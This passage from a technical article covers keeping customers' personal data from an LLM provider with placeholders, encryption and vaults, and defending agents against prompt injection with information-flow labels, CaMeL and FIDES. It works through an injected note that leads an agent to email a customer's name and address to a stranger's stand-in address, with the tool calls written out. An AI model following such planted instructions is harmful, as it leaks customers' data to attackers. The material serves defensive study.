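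The method is weak when there are few possible values. A thousand guesses at an encrypted value have a one-in-a-million chance of including the right Social Security number, but a one-in-a-hundred chance of including the right five-digit order number. Attacks on the cipher itself also become more practical, because they need a large amount of data encrypted under the same key, and an attacker may plausibly obtain it when the set of values is small. Dworkin and Mouha therefore require at least a million possible inputs. At that size, the known attacks on FF1 would need at least 2⁷⁷ pieces of data to recover one value. Order number 48213 and "Tom" both fall short of this minimum, since there are only 100,000 five-digit order numbers and 17,576 three-letter strings.

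Only FF1 remains of three NIST candidates. NIST dropped FF2 before publication, after the US National Security Agency warned that it was weaker than intended. Dworkin's *Recommendation for Block Cipher Modes of Operation* (2016) approved FF1 and FF3. Researchers published an attack on FF3 in 2017, NIST proposed a repaired version in 2019, and another attack in 2021 affected both versions.

The 2025 document, which removes FF3, is still a draft. As Dworkin and Mouha record, comments closed on 4 April 2025, and NIST lists no final version. The 2016 text therefore formally remains in force. It includes FF3, and it requires at least a hundred possible inputs but only recommends a million. Anyone choosing a method now should follow the draft. Ericsson's *Comments on NIST 800-38G* (2025) urged NIST to hold a competition for new algorithms because the draft leaves only one approved method.

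### How long a placeholder should last

If `[NAME_1]` stands for Maria Keller in both the ticket and the customer record, the model can connect her complaint to her purchase of the kettle. The model's provider can also see that the two texts concern the same person, and how often that person appears, without knowing who it is. The longer the placeholder stays the same, the more texts the provider can link.

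| Placeholder lasts for | What the model can link | What the provider can link | What the shop must keep |
|---|---|---|---|
| One message | Mentions within that message | The same mentions | A separate mapping for each message |
| One session | The ticket, the record and the later tool calls | Everything about Keller in that session | A vault or key until the session ends |
| Ever | Her earlier tickets and the agent's stored memory as well | Everything the agent ever reads about her | A vault or key indefinitely |

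Placeholders that last for one message work for a single question to a chatbot, but not for an agent. Each query contains the whole conversation, so if numbering restarts in every message, `[EMAIL_1]` can stand for Keller's address in one part of the prompt and someone else's in another. When the model then calls `email.send` with `[EMAIL_1]`, the harness cannot determine which address to restore.

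Permanent placeholders let an agent recognise a returning customer and let analysts count repeat complaints without seeing names. Permanence also makes each detection error more harmful. Suppose Keller appears as `[NAME_583]` in thirty tickets, and in one of them the detector misses her surname in the signature. The provider can then attach her name to all thirty. With a new placeholder for each session, the same error would expose one ticket.

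The choice between permanent and session-limited placeholders applies to keyed functions too. With one key and a fixed tweak, FF1 always turns Tom's number into the same string, so the placeholder is permanent. To limit the placeholder to a session, the harness has to change the key or the tweak for each session.

For the support agent, the best default is to keep each value's placeholder the same throughout a session. A session is long enough to connect the ticket, the record and the refund, and the shop can look up returning customers in its own database without placeholders.

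### Veil-Then-Reveal

*Veil-Then-Reveal* (Elmahallawy, Shaaban and Carroll, 2026) combines the two keyed methods and limits their results to one session. Its software runs on the user's device and derives new keys for each session from a master key and the session's identifier.

The software encrypts Social Security, phone and card numbers and dates with FF1. For names, places, organisations and email addresses, it uses a keyed hash to pick a surrogate from a list. For example, "Marie Curie" and "MARIE CURIE" both become "Ágnes Orosz" in one session, and "Marie Curie" becomes "Lucie Musil" in another. If a different person already has that surrogate, the software picks again, so two people never share one. A vault on the device stores the pairs of originals and surrogates and is empty once the session ends.

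The assumed adversary is an honest-but-curious provider, one that runs the model correctly but may store, study and compare everything it receives. It knows the design but not the keys, and it has no access to the user's device or vault. For the values that the detector finds, Elmahallawy and colleagues prove a bound. The adversary submits two prompts with the same surrounding text, the same formats and the same pattern of repeated values, receives one of them with surrogates, and has to tell which it was. Its advantage over guessing, across σ sessions, is at most

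2(σ + 1)(Adv<sub>HKDF</sub> + Adv<sub>FF1</sub> + Adv<sub>HMAC</sub>)

Each term in the second bracket is an attacker's advantage in distinguishing one component from a truly random function or permutation. HKDF derives the keys. If all three components are strong, the provider learns only what the surrogates are designed to preserve, such as a number's layout or whether two values are equal. It also cannot tell whether two sessions mention the same person, unless the surrounding text reveals it.

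The FF1 term is somewhat doubtful for dates. Encrypting a date's digits directly would usually give an impossible date, such as day 73 of month 41, so the software numbers the 73,049 days from 1900 to 2099, encrypts the number as five digits, and encrypts again if the result is out of range. Five digits allow only 100,000 values, a tenth of the minimum in NIST's draft. The practical risk is probably small, because each key lasts for one session and encrypts few dates.

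Encrypting each date separately also destroys the relation between dates. In one prompt, encryption moved an article from August 2014 to 1981 and its January 2017 update to 1909. The software can instead shift every date in a document by the same secret number of days, up to 4,000. In a test on 97 documents with two dates each, a model put the dates in the right order in 53.6% of cases with encryption and in all cases with shifting. When the model was asked for the date a week after the second one, its answer converted back to the correct date in 0% of cases with encryption and 97.9% with shifting. But shifting makes past events look like future ones, and vice versa, unless the software also shifts the current date in the prompt. If it does, a provider that knows today's date can work out the shift and recover every date.

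On 10,000 synthetic documents, the detector found 97.9% of 11,322 labelled values, counting any overlap as a find. The software replaced 95.2% of all the values it detected. Most of those it didn't replace were times, ages and phrases such as "next week", which has no digits to change. The software restored 99.9% of the replaced values exactly when no model had processed the text.

Real requests gave a much worse result. Elmahallawy and colleagues ran several systems on 664 messages that people had actually sent to a chatbot:

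| Method | Personal values that reach the provider | Requests with no exposed value | Words of the request kept |
|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 95.1% | 3.8% | 100% |
| Numbered placeholders (Rescriber) | 27.0% | 64.8% | 93% |
| Veil-Then-Reveal | 27.0% | 64.6% | 95% |
| Local model replaces values (Hide-and-Seek) | 19.8% | 69.3% | 86% |
| Local model rewrites the request (SEAL) | 0.2% | 99.4% | 13% |

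On a sample of 1,000 of the synthetic documents, 2.9% of values reached the provider. Rescriber and Veil-Then-Reveal both leaked 27.0% because they used the same detector and so missed the same values. The more sophisticated replacement produced natural-looking text but did not change how many values leaked. Replacement takes little time. The software spent a median of 0.057 seconds per request on the device, nearly all of it on detection. SEAL took more than a minute and discarded most of the request.

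It is less clear whether natural-looking text helps the model. With surrogates, the restored answers from Llama-3.2-3B, a small model from Meta, contained 38.2% of the real values from the prompts, compared with 38.4% without protection and 47.0% with numbered placeholders. Two other small models repeated surrogates more often than numbered placeholders. Elmahallawy and colleagues measured whether values came back but, apart from the date test, not whether the answers were right.

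The paper's own examples show how invented names can cause errors. One user asked which of several university programmes would best prepare him to become a technical leader at Boeing. The software replaced the universities and the company with invented names. The model recommended a combination anyway, and the software then inserted the real names into the advice, although the model had never received them. In another example, the software replaced Richmond Deckow with Samantha Leonard. The model wrote "her", and the pronoun stayed after the software restored the original name. The placeholder `[NAME_1]` would at least have avoided giving the model a false clue about gender.

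Elmahallawy and colleagues did not test tool calls, where an unrestored surrogate could do harm. Their software builds invented email addresses from common names and the domains of 15 widely used providers, so an invented address may belong to someone. If restoration failed and the support agent called `email.send` with one of these addresses, a stranger could receive the message about Keller's refund.

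## Carrying placeholders through the agent's work and restoring them

Software around a chatbot can restore the real values once, in the answer it shows to the user, but an agent's harness has to restore them each time a tool needs them and hide them again when the tool returns its result. Anthropic sketched how to do this in its November 2025 article on code execution with MCP.

### Two ways to keep data out of the model's context

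In Anthropic's example, an agent copies customers' contact details from a Google spreadsheet into Salesforce, a customer database. The model writes a short program that reads the rows and passes each one to Salesforce. The MCP client, the part of the application that exchanges messages with tool servers, intercepts the rows and replaces the personal values with placeholders. Obot's *Building with MCP* reproduces a record as the model would see it, with the Salesforce identifier unchanged and `[EMAIL_1]`, `[PHONE_1]` and `[NAME_1]` in the other fields. When the program calls the Salesforce tool, the client looks up the real values and puts them into the call, so Salesforce receives them without the model seeing them.

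The article also describes a way to hide data without placeholders. If the model writes a program instead of calling the tools one at a time, the results stay in the environment where the program runs, and the model sees only what the program prints or returns. For example, a program can read 10,000 spreadsheet rows and print five. Anthropic recommends this mainly because it is cheaper, and estimates that it cuts one task from 150,000 tokens to 2,000. How much privacy it gives depends on the program the model writes. A program that prints one row to check the column names puts that row into the context. With placeholders, the printed row would contain `[EMAIL_1]` instead of the email address.

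A developer can use placeholders or code execution alone. The shop's support agent makes ordinary tool calls, so it can use placeholders without running any code. If a developer uses both, the program that runs between two tool calls apparently handles placeholders too, because the client restores values only when the next call goes out. The program therefore cannot sort customers by surname or pick out the addresses at one company. A program working on the real values could do both, but the harness would then have to filter everything it prints. Anthropic also warns that running model-written code requires a sandbox, resource limits and monitoring. It gives no measurements of how well the placeholder mechanism works.

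### One ticket through the full cycle

When Maria Keller's ticket arrives, the harness replaces her name and address before the first query. The model reads that `[NAME_1]` wants her money back for the kettle in order 48213. It calls `crm.lookup` with the order number, which the harness left unchanged. The record contains Keller's name and address again, and the harness finds both in the vault and reuses their placeholders. The model calls `refund.issue` for 62.50 euros and then produces this call:

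```json
{
  "name": "email.send",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "[EMAIL_1]",
    "subject": "Refund for order 48213",
    "body": "Dear [NAME_1], we have refunded EUR 62.50 for your kettle."
  }
}
```

The harness checks that this tool is allowed to receive the real values, inserts them into a copy of the call and sends the copy to the mail server. The version with placeholders stays in the conversation. If the harness put the copy with real values there instead, the next query would send Keller's address to the model's provider.

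The mail server then returns a confirmation:

```json
{
  "content": [
    {
      "type": "text",
      "text": "Queued for Maria Keller <maria.keller@example.com>."
    }
  ],
  "isError": false
}
```

Many tools repeat their inputs like this. Adding the confirmation to the context unchanged would expose the personal data that the placeholders were hiding from the model. The harness therefore has to run the replacement again on every result, including those from tools that only send data out.

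Some published designs cover only part of this cycle. Strathweb's *PII guardrails for .NET applications* describes AgentGuard, a library that replaces personal values in tool results before the model reads them. In its example, a support agent looks up a customer and summarizes her contact details as `<EMAIL_ADDRESS>` and `+1 <PHONE_NUMBER>`. These placeholders are irreversible, so the person who asked for the details doesn't get them. AgentGuard also has a reversible mode, but the article demonstrates it only for the reply to the user, not for tool calls.

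mcp-pvp's *Privacy Vault Protocol (PVP) v1*, a draft specification, has the opposite gap. Its vault inserts the real values just as the tool runs and returns the tool's result to the agent, but the draft has no step that replaces values in that result. It assumes a mail tool that returns only a message number. With the shop's mail server, the address would go straight back to the model.

### Nested arguments, errors and logs

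In the call above, `[EMAIL_1]` fills a whole field, while `[NAME_1]` is in the middle of a sentence. Other tools accept lists of recipients or nested records, so the harness has to search inside every string at every level of the arguments. The preferred form for a hidden value in mcp-pvp is a small JSON object with an identifier and a type. These objects are easy to find and check, but the draft describes insertion only for them and doesn't explain how Keller's name would get into the text of the email.

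The harness should parse the tool call before it restores any values. If it pasted a company name such as Keller "Home" Ltd. into the raw JSON, the first quotation mark in the name would end the string early and break the call. After parsing, the harness can replace the placeholder without breaking the JSON. Tools that take a database query or shell command as a single string remain dangerous, because the restored value becomes part of the command. A customer could enter a command as his name, and it wouldn't reach the model or a scanner that runs before restoration. A tool that takes the value as a separate parameter avoids this problem.

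Error messages also repeat inputs, often in a different form. A mail server might return an error containing `MARIA.KELLER@EXAMPLE.COM`, or a web service one containing `maria.keller%40example.com`. A search for the exact string stored in the vault would miss both, so the harness should ignore case, decode percent-encoded text and also run the detector. Developers can easily overlook error messages, because a tool that crashes may return its error through different code from an ordinary result.

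If restoration fails, the model needs an explanation that omits the value. mcp-pvp defines separate error codes for an unknown placeholder, an expired session and a refusal by policy. The reason given in its sample refusal is that `send_email` accepts email addresses only in the recipient fields, which is enough for the model to correct the call.

Logs should contain the call before placeholders are restored to real values and the result after real values are replaced with placeholders. mcp-pvp forbids real values in the vault's logs. Its audit entries record the tool, the field, the type of value and whether the vault allowed the disclosure. An investigator could see from these entries that an email address went to `email.send`, but would need the vault to identify whose address it was. If the shop empties the vault after each session, only the mail server's log still shows who received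 the message.

### Several turns, memory and sub-agents

To keep replacements consistent over several turns, Panjwani (2026), in *CAMP*, keeps a registry of all personal values that the detector has found in a session, and gives each value one surrogate for the whole session. However, CAMP leaves most values in place until a risk score reaches a threshold. Every type of data has a weight *w*, such as 0.60 for names and 0.80 for email addresses. The score adds up the types that have appeared so far:

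Σ *w* × (1 + 0.3 × *d*)

Here *d* is the number of other types in the session. A name and an email address together score (0.60 + 0.80) × 1.3 = 1.82. Panjwani considers 2.0 a reasonable threshold, so Keller's name and email address would both go to the provider unchanged. A phone number, with a weight of 0.75, would raise the score to 2.15 × 1.6 = 3.44. CAMP would then rewrite the whole conversation with surrogates, but the provider would already have the name and email address.

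Panjwani reports that CAMP reduced exposure to zero in four synthetic conversations. But the rewriting began between turns 2 and 5, and CAMP sends earlier messages unmodified, except for card numbers and a few similar identifiers that it always blocks. The reported zero can therefore apply only to what the model received once rewriting began. The shop's agent should keep the registry but drop the threshold, so that it replaces values starting with the first message.

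Memory lasts longer than a session, so numbering that restarts with each session would make `[EMAIL_1]` in an old note ambiguous. Chen, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *MemPrivacy*, keep the mapping in a database on the user's device, so that a placeholder in the provider's memory keeps its meaning across sessions. They tested this with three systems that store and retrieve facts from past conversations. GPT-4.1 ran all three and answered 615 questions about 40 synthetic users. Its accuracy was:

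| Memory system | Original text | Typed placeholders | Untyped placeholders | Asterisks, no restoration |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangMem | 65.4% | 64.1% | 58.7% | 38.7% |
| Mem0 | 68.6% | 67.9% | 63.9% | 26.8% |
| Memobase | 38.6% | 37.9% | 33.9% | 21.6% |

Typed placeholders such as `<EMAIL_1>` lowered scores by at most 1.3 points on this benchmark and 1.6 points on a second one. Untyped placeholders such as `<Mask_1>` lowered scores by up to 8.7 points.

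The small losses depended on the detector, which Chen and colleagues had trained on conversations from the same generator as the test. When they used GPT-5.2 as the detector instead, accuracy on Mem0 with typed placeholders fell to 32.2%, far below the 63.9% for untyped placeholders with their own detector. Detection quality thus mattered more in this test than the form of the placeholder. The test covered only questions and answers, but an agent that acts on its memory also has to put the placeholder into a tool call.

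The shop could avoid the linking that permanent placeholders allow by keeping the agent's notes on its own servers. When the harness loads a note, it would replace the stored identifiers with the current session's placeholders. The system in *What to Remember, What to Reveal* (2026) also keeps exact values in protected storage, separate from the cleaned text in searchable memory. It restores a value only if the task needs it and the user authorizes it.

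Sub-agents create a similar numbering problem. A main agent may delegate the refund to a sub-agent, a second model run with its own context. *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in LLM agents, notes that collaboration between agents adds places where they read, write or transmit data. If the sub-agent's harness has no access to the main agent's vault, it cannot restore `[NAME_1]`. If it starts its own vault, its `[NAME_1]` may refer to another customer, and the main harness could insert Keller's name into a result about that customer. mcp-pvp uses random identifiers valid for one session, so the same mix-up produces an error instead of a wrong name. Panjwani leaves sub-agents to future work.

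### How placeholders get damaged

Restoration works only if the harness can recognize the placeholders in the model's output. Beskorovainyi tested this on 190 of his synthetic documents in each language. Two small models that he ran on his own computer, qwen3.5:9b and gemma4:12b, wrote a summary and a reply letter for each document, which gave 760 answers per language.

In UK English, his engine met the threshold of restoring at least 99% of placeholders. The scoring program counted one failure in the 760 answers, but a manual check showed that this was a scoring error. The models had altered 65 placeholders, and the engine recognized and restored all of them.

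In Russian, the engine correctly restored only 94.6% of name placeholders with the weaker of the two models, and about a quarter of the answers contained at least one wrong name. The models had mostly copied the placeholders correctly, but Russian names change their endings according to their role in the sentence, so the engine has to inflect each name when it restores it. Of the 288 failures in Russian, 188 came from the inflection code in pii-guard, the Russian tool on which the engine builds. For example, it wrote the plural "Kharitony" instead of "Kharitonov". In another 82 cases, the engine had stored the name incorrectly.

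A name in an email needs the correct grammatical ending, but a database search usually needs the name's basic form. Faulty inflection would therefore affect email text more than lookup arguments, while a wrongly stored name would affect both.

Beskorovainyi's tests with his own engine and other tools also show the damage that models do themselves:

| Damage | Example | What the harness can do |
|---|---|---|
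| The model alters a placeholder | gemma4:12b expanded an address placeholder to `[RECIPIENT_ADDRESS_1]` | Match it by type and number, or reject the call |
| The model drops placeholders | With pii-guard's own prompt, qwen3.5:9b used none of its tags in 25 of 40 answers | Reject a call in which a required field is empty |
| The model invents a placeholder | qwen3.5:9b wrote 106 that the engine had never issued, such as `[ORG_2]` for an organisation the document didn't name | Reject any placeholder that is not in the vault |

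Whether an altered placeholder can be restored depends on the software that reads the answer. In one answer, gemma4:12b left the closing slash out of 29 of pii-guard's XML-style tags. pii-guard's strict parser lost all 29 values, but a more tolerant parser restored them. Tolerant parsing doesn't work for long encrypted strings. AgentGuard's reversible mode turns a short email address into 64 characters and restores it only on an exact match, so one wrong character loses the address.

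*PromptGraph* (Gu, Wan and colleagues, 2026) is strict by design. Its software restores a placeholder only if the identifier is in a local table and the placeholder passes a consistency check against data stored with that entry. Placeholders that the model has rewritten or invented stay unresolved. In a letter, this leaves a visible gap. Strictness does less harm in a tool call, because the harness can return an error before the call runs and let the model try again. A tolerant parser that guessed the wrong recipient could send Keller's refund message to someone else.

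Neither kind of parser would detect a valid placeholder that stands for the wrong person. An early version of Beskorovainyi's engine gave people with the same surname the same placeholder, so a landlord and a tenant became the same party. He considers this worse than a leak because a user is unlikely to notice it. His restoration score would not have detected it either.

These results come from summaries and letters, and Beskorovainyi cautions that larger hosted models may treat placeholders differently. Copying one address into one field may be easier than writing a letter with thirty placeholders, but an agent may have to make hundreds of such copies.

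A search found no measurements of how often agents complete whole tasks with PII placeholders. The closest result is for file paths. *SlotGuard* (2026) replayed 160 tasks in which a model had to select the right local file for a tool. With generic redaction, no model selected the exact path. Placeholders in the style of an existing tool, VibeGuard, raised the success rate to between 26.9% and 36.9%. With SlotGuard's full method, 92.5% to 97.5% of the outputs were valid for the tool, close to the rate with the original paths, although a valid path can still be the wrong one. The 160 tasks are variations on 40 paths, and none ran from start to finish. The results still show that a placeholder scheme can leave the text readable but make most tool calls fail.

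### Tasks that need the real value

Some tasks fail even if the model copies every placeholder correctly. Suppose a customer named Keller writes that the parcel label said "Keler" and asks the shop to correct it. If the harness gives the two spellings different placeholders, the model can pass the right one to a tool that updates the record, but it cannot tell what the mistake was. If the harness gives both the same placeholder, the model reads that `[NAME_1]` should be `[NAME_1]`, and the request makes no sense.

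The model also cannot compute an age from `[BIRTHDATE_1]`, sort customers alphabetically or notice that an address ends in ".con". It may answer anyway, since nothing forces it to report that the value is missing. The large losses that Deußer and colleagues measured on questions about retrieved documents are a broader case of the same problem, because the answers depended on names and facts that the software had hidden.

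A tool that computes on the hidden value should solve many of these cases. If the shop sells kitchen knives only to adults, the model could make this call:

```json
{
  "name": "customer.is_adult",
  "arguments": { "birthdate": "[BIRTHDATE_1]" }
}
```

The harness restores the date, the tool compares it with today's date, and the model receives only `true` or `false`. Similar tools could compare two spellings, check the format of an address or count the days since a delivery. The developer has to foresee which questions the agent will need to answer, and any other question still requires the real value or a person.

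Each tool should also be limited to a narrow question. A tool that returned the customer's age would reveal more than the shop needs. If a tool accepted any cut-off date, repeated calls could reveal the customer's birth date, because 16 yes-or-no answers are enough to identify one day in a century. `customer.is_adult` has a fixed cut-off, so calling it again on the same day reveals nothing more.

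## Deciding where a real value may go

In the refund example, the harness checked only that `email.send` may receive personal data before it restored Maria Keller's address. The model chose the recipient and wrote the text. Anyone who can influence the model can therefore influence where the restored values go.

### A real address in the wrong email

Suppose the stranger's message among the notes on Keller's record asks for the customer's name and email address to be sent to claims@parcel-desk.example, supposedly for the courier's insurance. When `crm.lookup` returns the record, the harness replaces Keller's details as it should. It also replaces the stranger's address, which becomes `[EMAIL_2]`. A model that follows the note then produces this call:

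```json
{
  "name": "email.send",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "[EMAIL_2]",
    "subject": "Order 48213",
    "body": "Customer: [NAME_1], [EMAIL_1]"
  }
}
```

All three placeholders are in the vault, and the tool is allowed to receive real values. A harness that restores every placeholder fills them in, and the mail server delivers Keller's name and address to the stranger, even though the model never saw either address.

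This is the confused-deputy problem again, with the harness as the deputy. The harness is authorized to read the vault and the stranger isn't, but the harness uses that authority for whoever shaped the call. Nothing in the call shows whether Keller's ticket or the stranger's note led to it.

Tokenization still keeps a model from disguising a hidden value to get it past a filter. A model that has read an address can write it backwards, encode it in Base64, paraphrase it or hide it in the URL of a web search. If the model has only `[EMAIL_1]`, it can disclose the address only through restoration, where ordinary code can apply a rule. This holds only for values the detector found, and only if no tool returns the value in another form. If the harness restored values for a tool that converts text to Base64, the result would contain Keller's address in a form that the detector would probably miss.

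Tokenization does not prevent an agent from refunding order 48213 twice or deleting a record, because neither call needs a hidden value for the harness to restore.

### Restoring only under a rule

The harness should restore a real value only if a rule permits it, and refuse otherwise. Each rule should name the type of data, the tool, the argument and the destination. Anthropic briefly mentions that its placeholder design can also enforce deterministic rules about where data may flow, but gives no format for them.

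mcp-pvp does have a format. It is a small open-source project. Yohannes, in *mcp-pvp*, recounts that the idea came from a customer-support agent whose prompts, debug logs, conversation history and tool responses all held customers' details in plain text. Under the mcp-pvp draft, a restoration goes as follows:

1. The vault opens a session with an unguessable identifier and an expiry time.
2. The agent sends the vault a complete tool call that contains placeholders.
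3. The vault looks for a policy rule that allows this type of data in this argument of this tool. If there is none, it refuses.
4. The vault checks a capability, which is a signed authorization for one placeholder to go to one argument of one tool for a limited time.
5. The vault inserts the value and runs the tool itself, or hands the call to a trusted program on the same machine.

The draft also has a fallback operation that returns the real value to the caller, but it recommends delivery inside the vault so that the value never returns to the agent. The draft limits how many values and bytes the vault may disclose in one step. An injected call requesting a hundred customers' addresses would exceed that limit.

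The draft's example rule lets `send_email` receive email addresses in the `to`, `cc` and `bcc` fields. This would block the stranger's call, because `[EMAIL_1]` is in the body. But the stranger can change his note to ask for an email to `[EMAIL_2]` with `[EMAIL_1]` in `cc`. Both placeholders are now in permitted fields, and the rule restricts only the type, tool and argument, not the destination, so it allows the call. The stranger can then read Keller's address in the header of the message he receives.

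The signature doesn't help here, because a valid capability shows only that the call fits the policy, not that anyone entitled to send the email wanted it sent. mcp-pvp's *Threat Model*, which covers version 0.6, explains that the vault now issues capabilities itself during delivery, for the tool and argument that the call names. This fixed a serious flaw in version 0.1, which handed out a wildcard capability along with the placeholders, so that anyone who intercepted the capability could obtain any value. The change also stops a model from using an invented placeholder.

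The threat model claims protection against prompt injection, but its scenario covers an attacker who asks the model to reveal an address, not one who has the address mailed to him. It excludes malicious tools, permissive policies and values that the detector misses. It also describes a feature added since the draft, which replaces personal values in tool results before the agent receives them. The makers' walkthrough on Ready Tensor describes disclosure to a model as permanently blocked, but the threat model warns that a careless policy can allow it, so an adopter should test this.

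### One rule for the shop

For the support agent, a rule with a destination could look like this:

```json
{
  "default": "refuse",
  "allow": [
    {
      "types": ["NAME", "EMAIL"],
      "tool": "email.send",
      "arguments": ["to", "body"],
      "destination": "record_owner"
    }
  ]
}
```

Here `record_owner` requires every recipient of the message to be the address in the `email` field of the customer record that the value came from. The vault therefore has to store which record the harness found each value in.

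The legitimate call goes to `[EMAIL_1]` and begins "Dear [NAME_1]". Both values come from Keller's record, and the only recipient is the address in its `email` field, so the harness restores them. The injected call is addressed to `[EMAIL_2]`, the stranger's address. That address also comes from Keller's record, but from the note instead of the `email` field, so the harness refuses. It also refuses the version with Keller in `cc`, because the stranger is still a recipient.

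The destination has to come from a source that the attacker cannot change. A rule that allowed email to whoever opened the ticket would fail if the stranger opened a ticket himself and quoted order 48213. `crm.lookup` would return Keller's record, and the agent's reply would send him her details. The `record_owner` rule would fail in the same way if the agent had a tool for updating customers' addresses, because an injected call could first replace Keller's address with the stranger's.

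The rule also covers only values that have been replaced with placeholders. Suppose the stranger asks what the customer bought and spells out his own address so that the detector misses it. The model can write that address into a tool call itself and add that order 48213 was a kettle for 62.50 euros. The call contains no placeholders, so there is nothing to restore.

### Labels on every value

Information-flow control, a technique much older than language models, deals with this by labelling all data, including the kettle and its price. Microsoft's FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe, uses labels with two parts. One part records whether the source is trusted, and the other lists who may read the value. In the shop, the labels could be:

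| Value | Source | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `email` field | Trusted | Staff, Keller |
| Order and price | Trusted | Staff, Keller |
| Stranger's note | Untrusted | Staff |

When software combines two values *x* and *y*, only people who may read both may read the result:

readers(*xy*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

The result is trusted only if both parts are. A summary of the whole record is therefore untrusted, and only staff may read it.

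Costa and colleagues build their rules from two policies. The first permits a consequential tool call only if the decision to make it and its arguments depend on trusted data alone. The second permits a call to send a value only if everyone who would receive it is among its permitted readers:

recipients ⊆ readers

The first policy blocks another refund that the note prompted. The second blocks the email about the kettle, although the email contains no placeholder. Costa and colleagues point out that the second policy alone doesn't prevent prompt injection, since untrusted text can still influence the call, but it limits what the attack can disclose.

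Once a model has read a record and written a tool call, software cannot tell which parts of the record influenced the call. The safe assumption is that all of them did, but then a single untrusted note makes everything the model does afterwards untrusted. When Costa and colleagues enforced their policies on an ordinary agent under this assumption, it completed 37.5% of banking tasks instead of 98.8%. CaMeL and FIDES avoid much of this loss by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the tool calls.

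### CaMeL

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, builds on the Dual LLM pattern that the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. In that pattern, a privileged model can use tools and reads only the user's request, while a quarantined model without tools reads the untrusted text. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's results by names such as `$email-summary-1`, much as the shop's model uses `[EMAIL_1]`.

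Willison's *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains the flaw that DeepMind found in his pattern. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. An attacker who can edit the notes cannot change the plan but can change the address that the quarantined model extracts. The privileged model then sends the document to the attacker, just as the shop's harness sent Keller's address to the stranger.

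CaMeL adds labels and an interpreter that enforces them. Suppose an employee of the shop asks the agent to refund order 48213 and email the customer a confirmation. The privileged model might write:

```python
record = crm_lookup(order="48213")
refund_issue(order="48213", amount=record.amount_eur)
address = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find the customer's email address", record)
email_send(to=address, body="We have refunded your order.")
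```

1. The privileged model writes the whole program from the employee's request, before anyone looks up the record.
2. A custom interpreter runs the program, which may use only a restricted part of the Python language, and calls the tools.
3. The quarantined model reads the record and returns an email address. If the stranger's note misleads it, it can return the wrong address, but it cannot add a step to the program.
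4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and permitted readers. `address` depends on the whole record, including the note, so it is untrusted.
5. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function receives the tool, the arguments and their labels, and allows or denies the call. If the policy for `email_send` requires a trusted recipient, the interpreter stops at the last line or asks the employee.

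If the program had read the address from `record.email` instead of asking the quarantined model for it, the address could have kept its field's trusted label, and the email would have gone out.

Willison notes that because the privileged model never receives tool results, its provider doesn't either. A smaller quarantined model could run on the user's own machine, which would hide the entire record from the outside provider, including personal data that a detector would miss.

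DeepMind tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated environments: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the chat service Slack. The benchmark's attacks place instructions in the data the agent reads. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives CaMeL's completion rate as 67%, while *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) gives 77%. The figures probably come from successive versions of DeepMind's paper.

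Two attacks counted as successful in DeepMind's evaluation, and *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) explains both. In one, the user had told the agent to make a payment described in a document, a case that CaMeL's threat model excludes. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews that contained the attacker's recommendation. AgentDojo's scoring searched for that text, so it counted the quote as a successful attack. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) reports the same scoring artefact as the only failure of a different system, TACIT, which enforces information-flow rules through a programming language's type system. TACIT completed about as many tasks as CaMeL without splitting the agent into two models.

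Later tests of CaMeL confirm its security but found lower completion rates:

- In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks without an attack. SecureClaw, the system that the paper proposes, completed 59. The comparison used an adapted version of CaMeL, so the adaptation may account for some of the loss.
- Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model from Anthropic, and it completed 49 of the 97 tasks. Both CaMeL and their extension of it blocked 17 tasks, although no attacker was present. Another 22 failed under both because the program didn't do what the user had asked, which a stronger model might fix.

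*The LLMbda Calculus* also reports that in one category of attacks on the model MiMo-v2.5, 138 of 141 succeeded with policy checking off, and none did with it on. Most of the protection in that category came from the policies, not from the separation of the two models. The separation failed in two trials where the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that translated each instruction in the file into a tool call, which let the file's author choose the calls.

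CaMeL checks each call only when the program reaches it. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check of the whole program before any tool runs, which can also cover the order of steps. The shop could require, for example, that a refund always come before the email confirming it. The researchers could express 22 of 28 AgentDojo policies in this form. Most of the rest depend on facts known only at run time, such as who can read a shared file.

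### FIDES

FIDES keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the model sees one result before it chooses the next call. On Keller's ticket, it would work like this:

1. Code around each tool labels the fields it returns. `email` and `amount_eur` are trusted, while the note and the text of the ticket are untrusted.
2. FIDES shows the model the trusted fields. It stores each untrusted field in a variable and shows the model only a name, such as `#crm_lookup_0.note#`.
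3. The model can pass that name to a tool. FIDES then inserts the content, which keeps its label.
4. If the model needs a fact from hidden text, it can put a question to an isolated model without tools. The answer goes into a new variable that inherits the labels.
5. The model can also open a variable and read it. From then on its context counts as untrusted, which restricts the calls it can make.
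6. Before each tool call, a policy engine checks the labels against the policies.

The shop's model could restrict the form of the answer in step 4, for example by asking whether the customer reports damage and accepting only yes or no. The model has to open the answer to act on it, but a policy can allow a refund based on a single untrusted bit, because one bit cannot carry an instruction. A dishonest customer can still get a "yes" by lying, as he could with a human clerk, but he cannot choose the amount or the recipient.

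The variables resemble placeholders, but their purpose is to keep attackers' text from the model. In Costa and colleagues' evaluation, FIDES didn't hide data merely because it was confidential. Costa and colleagues assume in their threat model that no adversary sees what goes to the model. Keller's address would be a trusted field, so the model's provider would receive it unless the shop also used PII tokenization.

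With GPT-4o, a model from 2024, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent in Costa and colleagues' test. FIDES with its policies switched off allowed 21, and with the policies on it allowed none. AgentDojo's own scoring counted three successes against FIDES, which Costa and colleagues rejected after reading the transcripts. These are the shares of tasks completed without an attack:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
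|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
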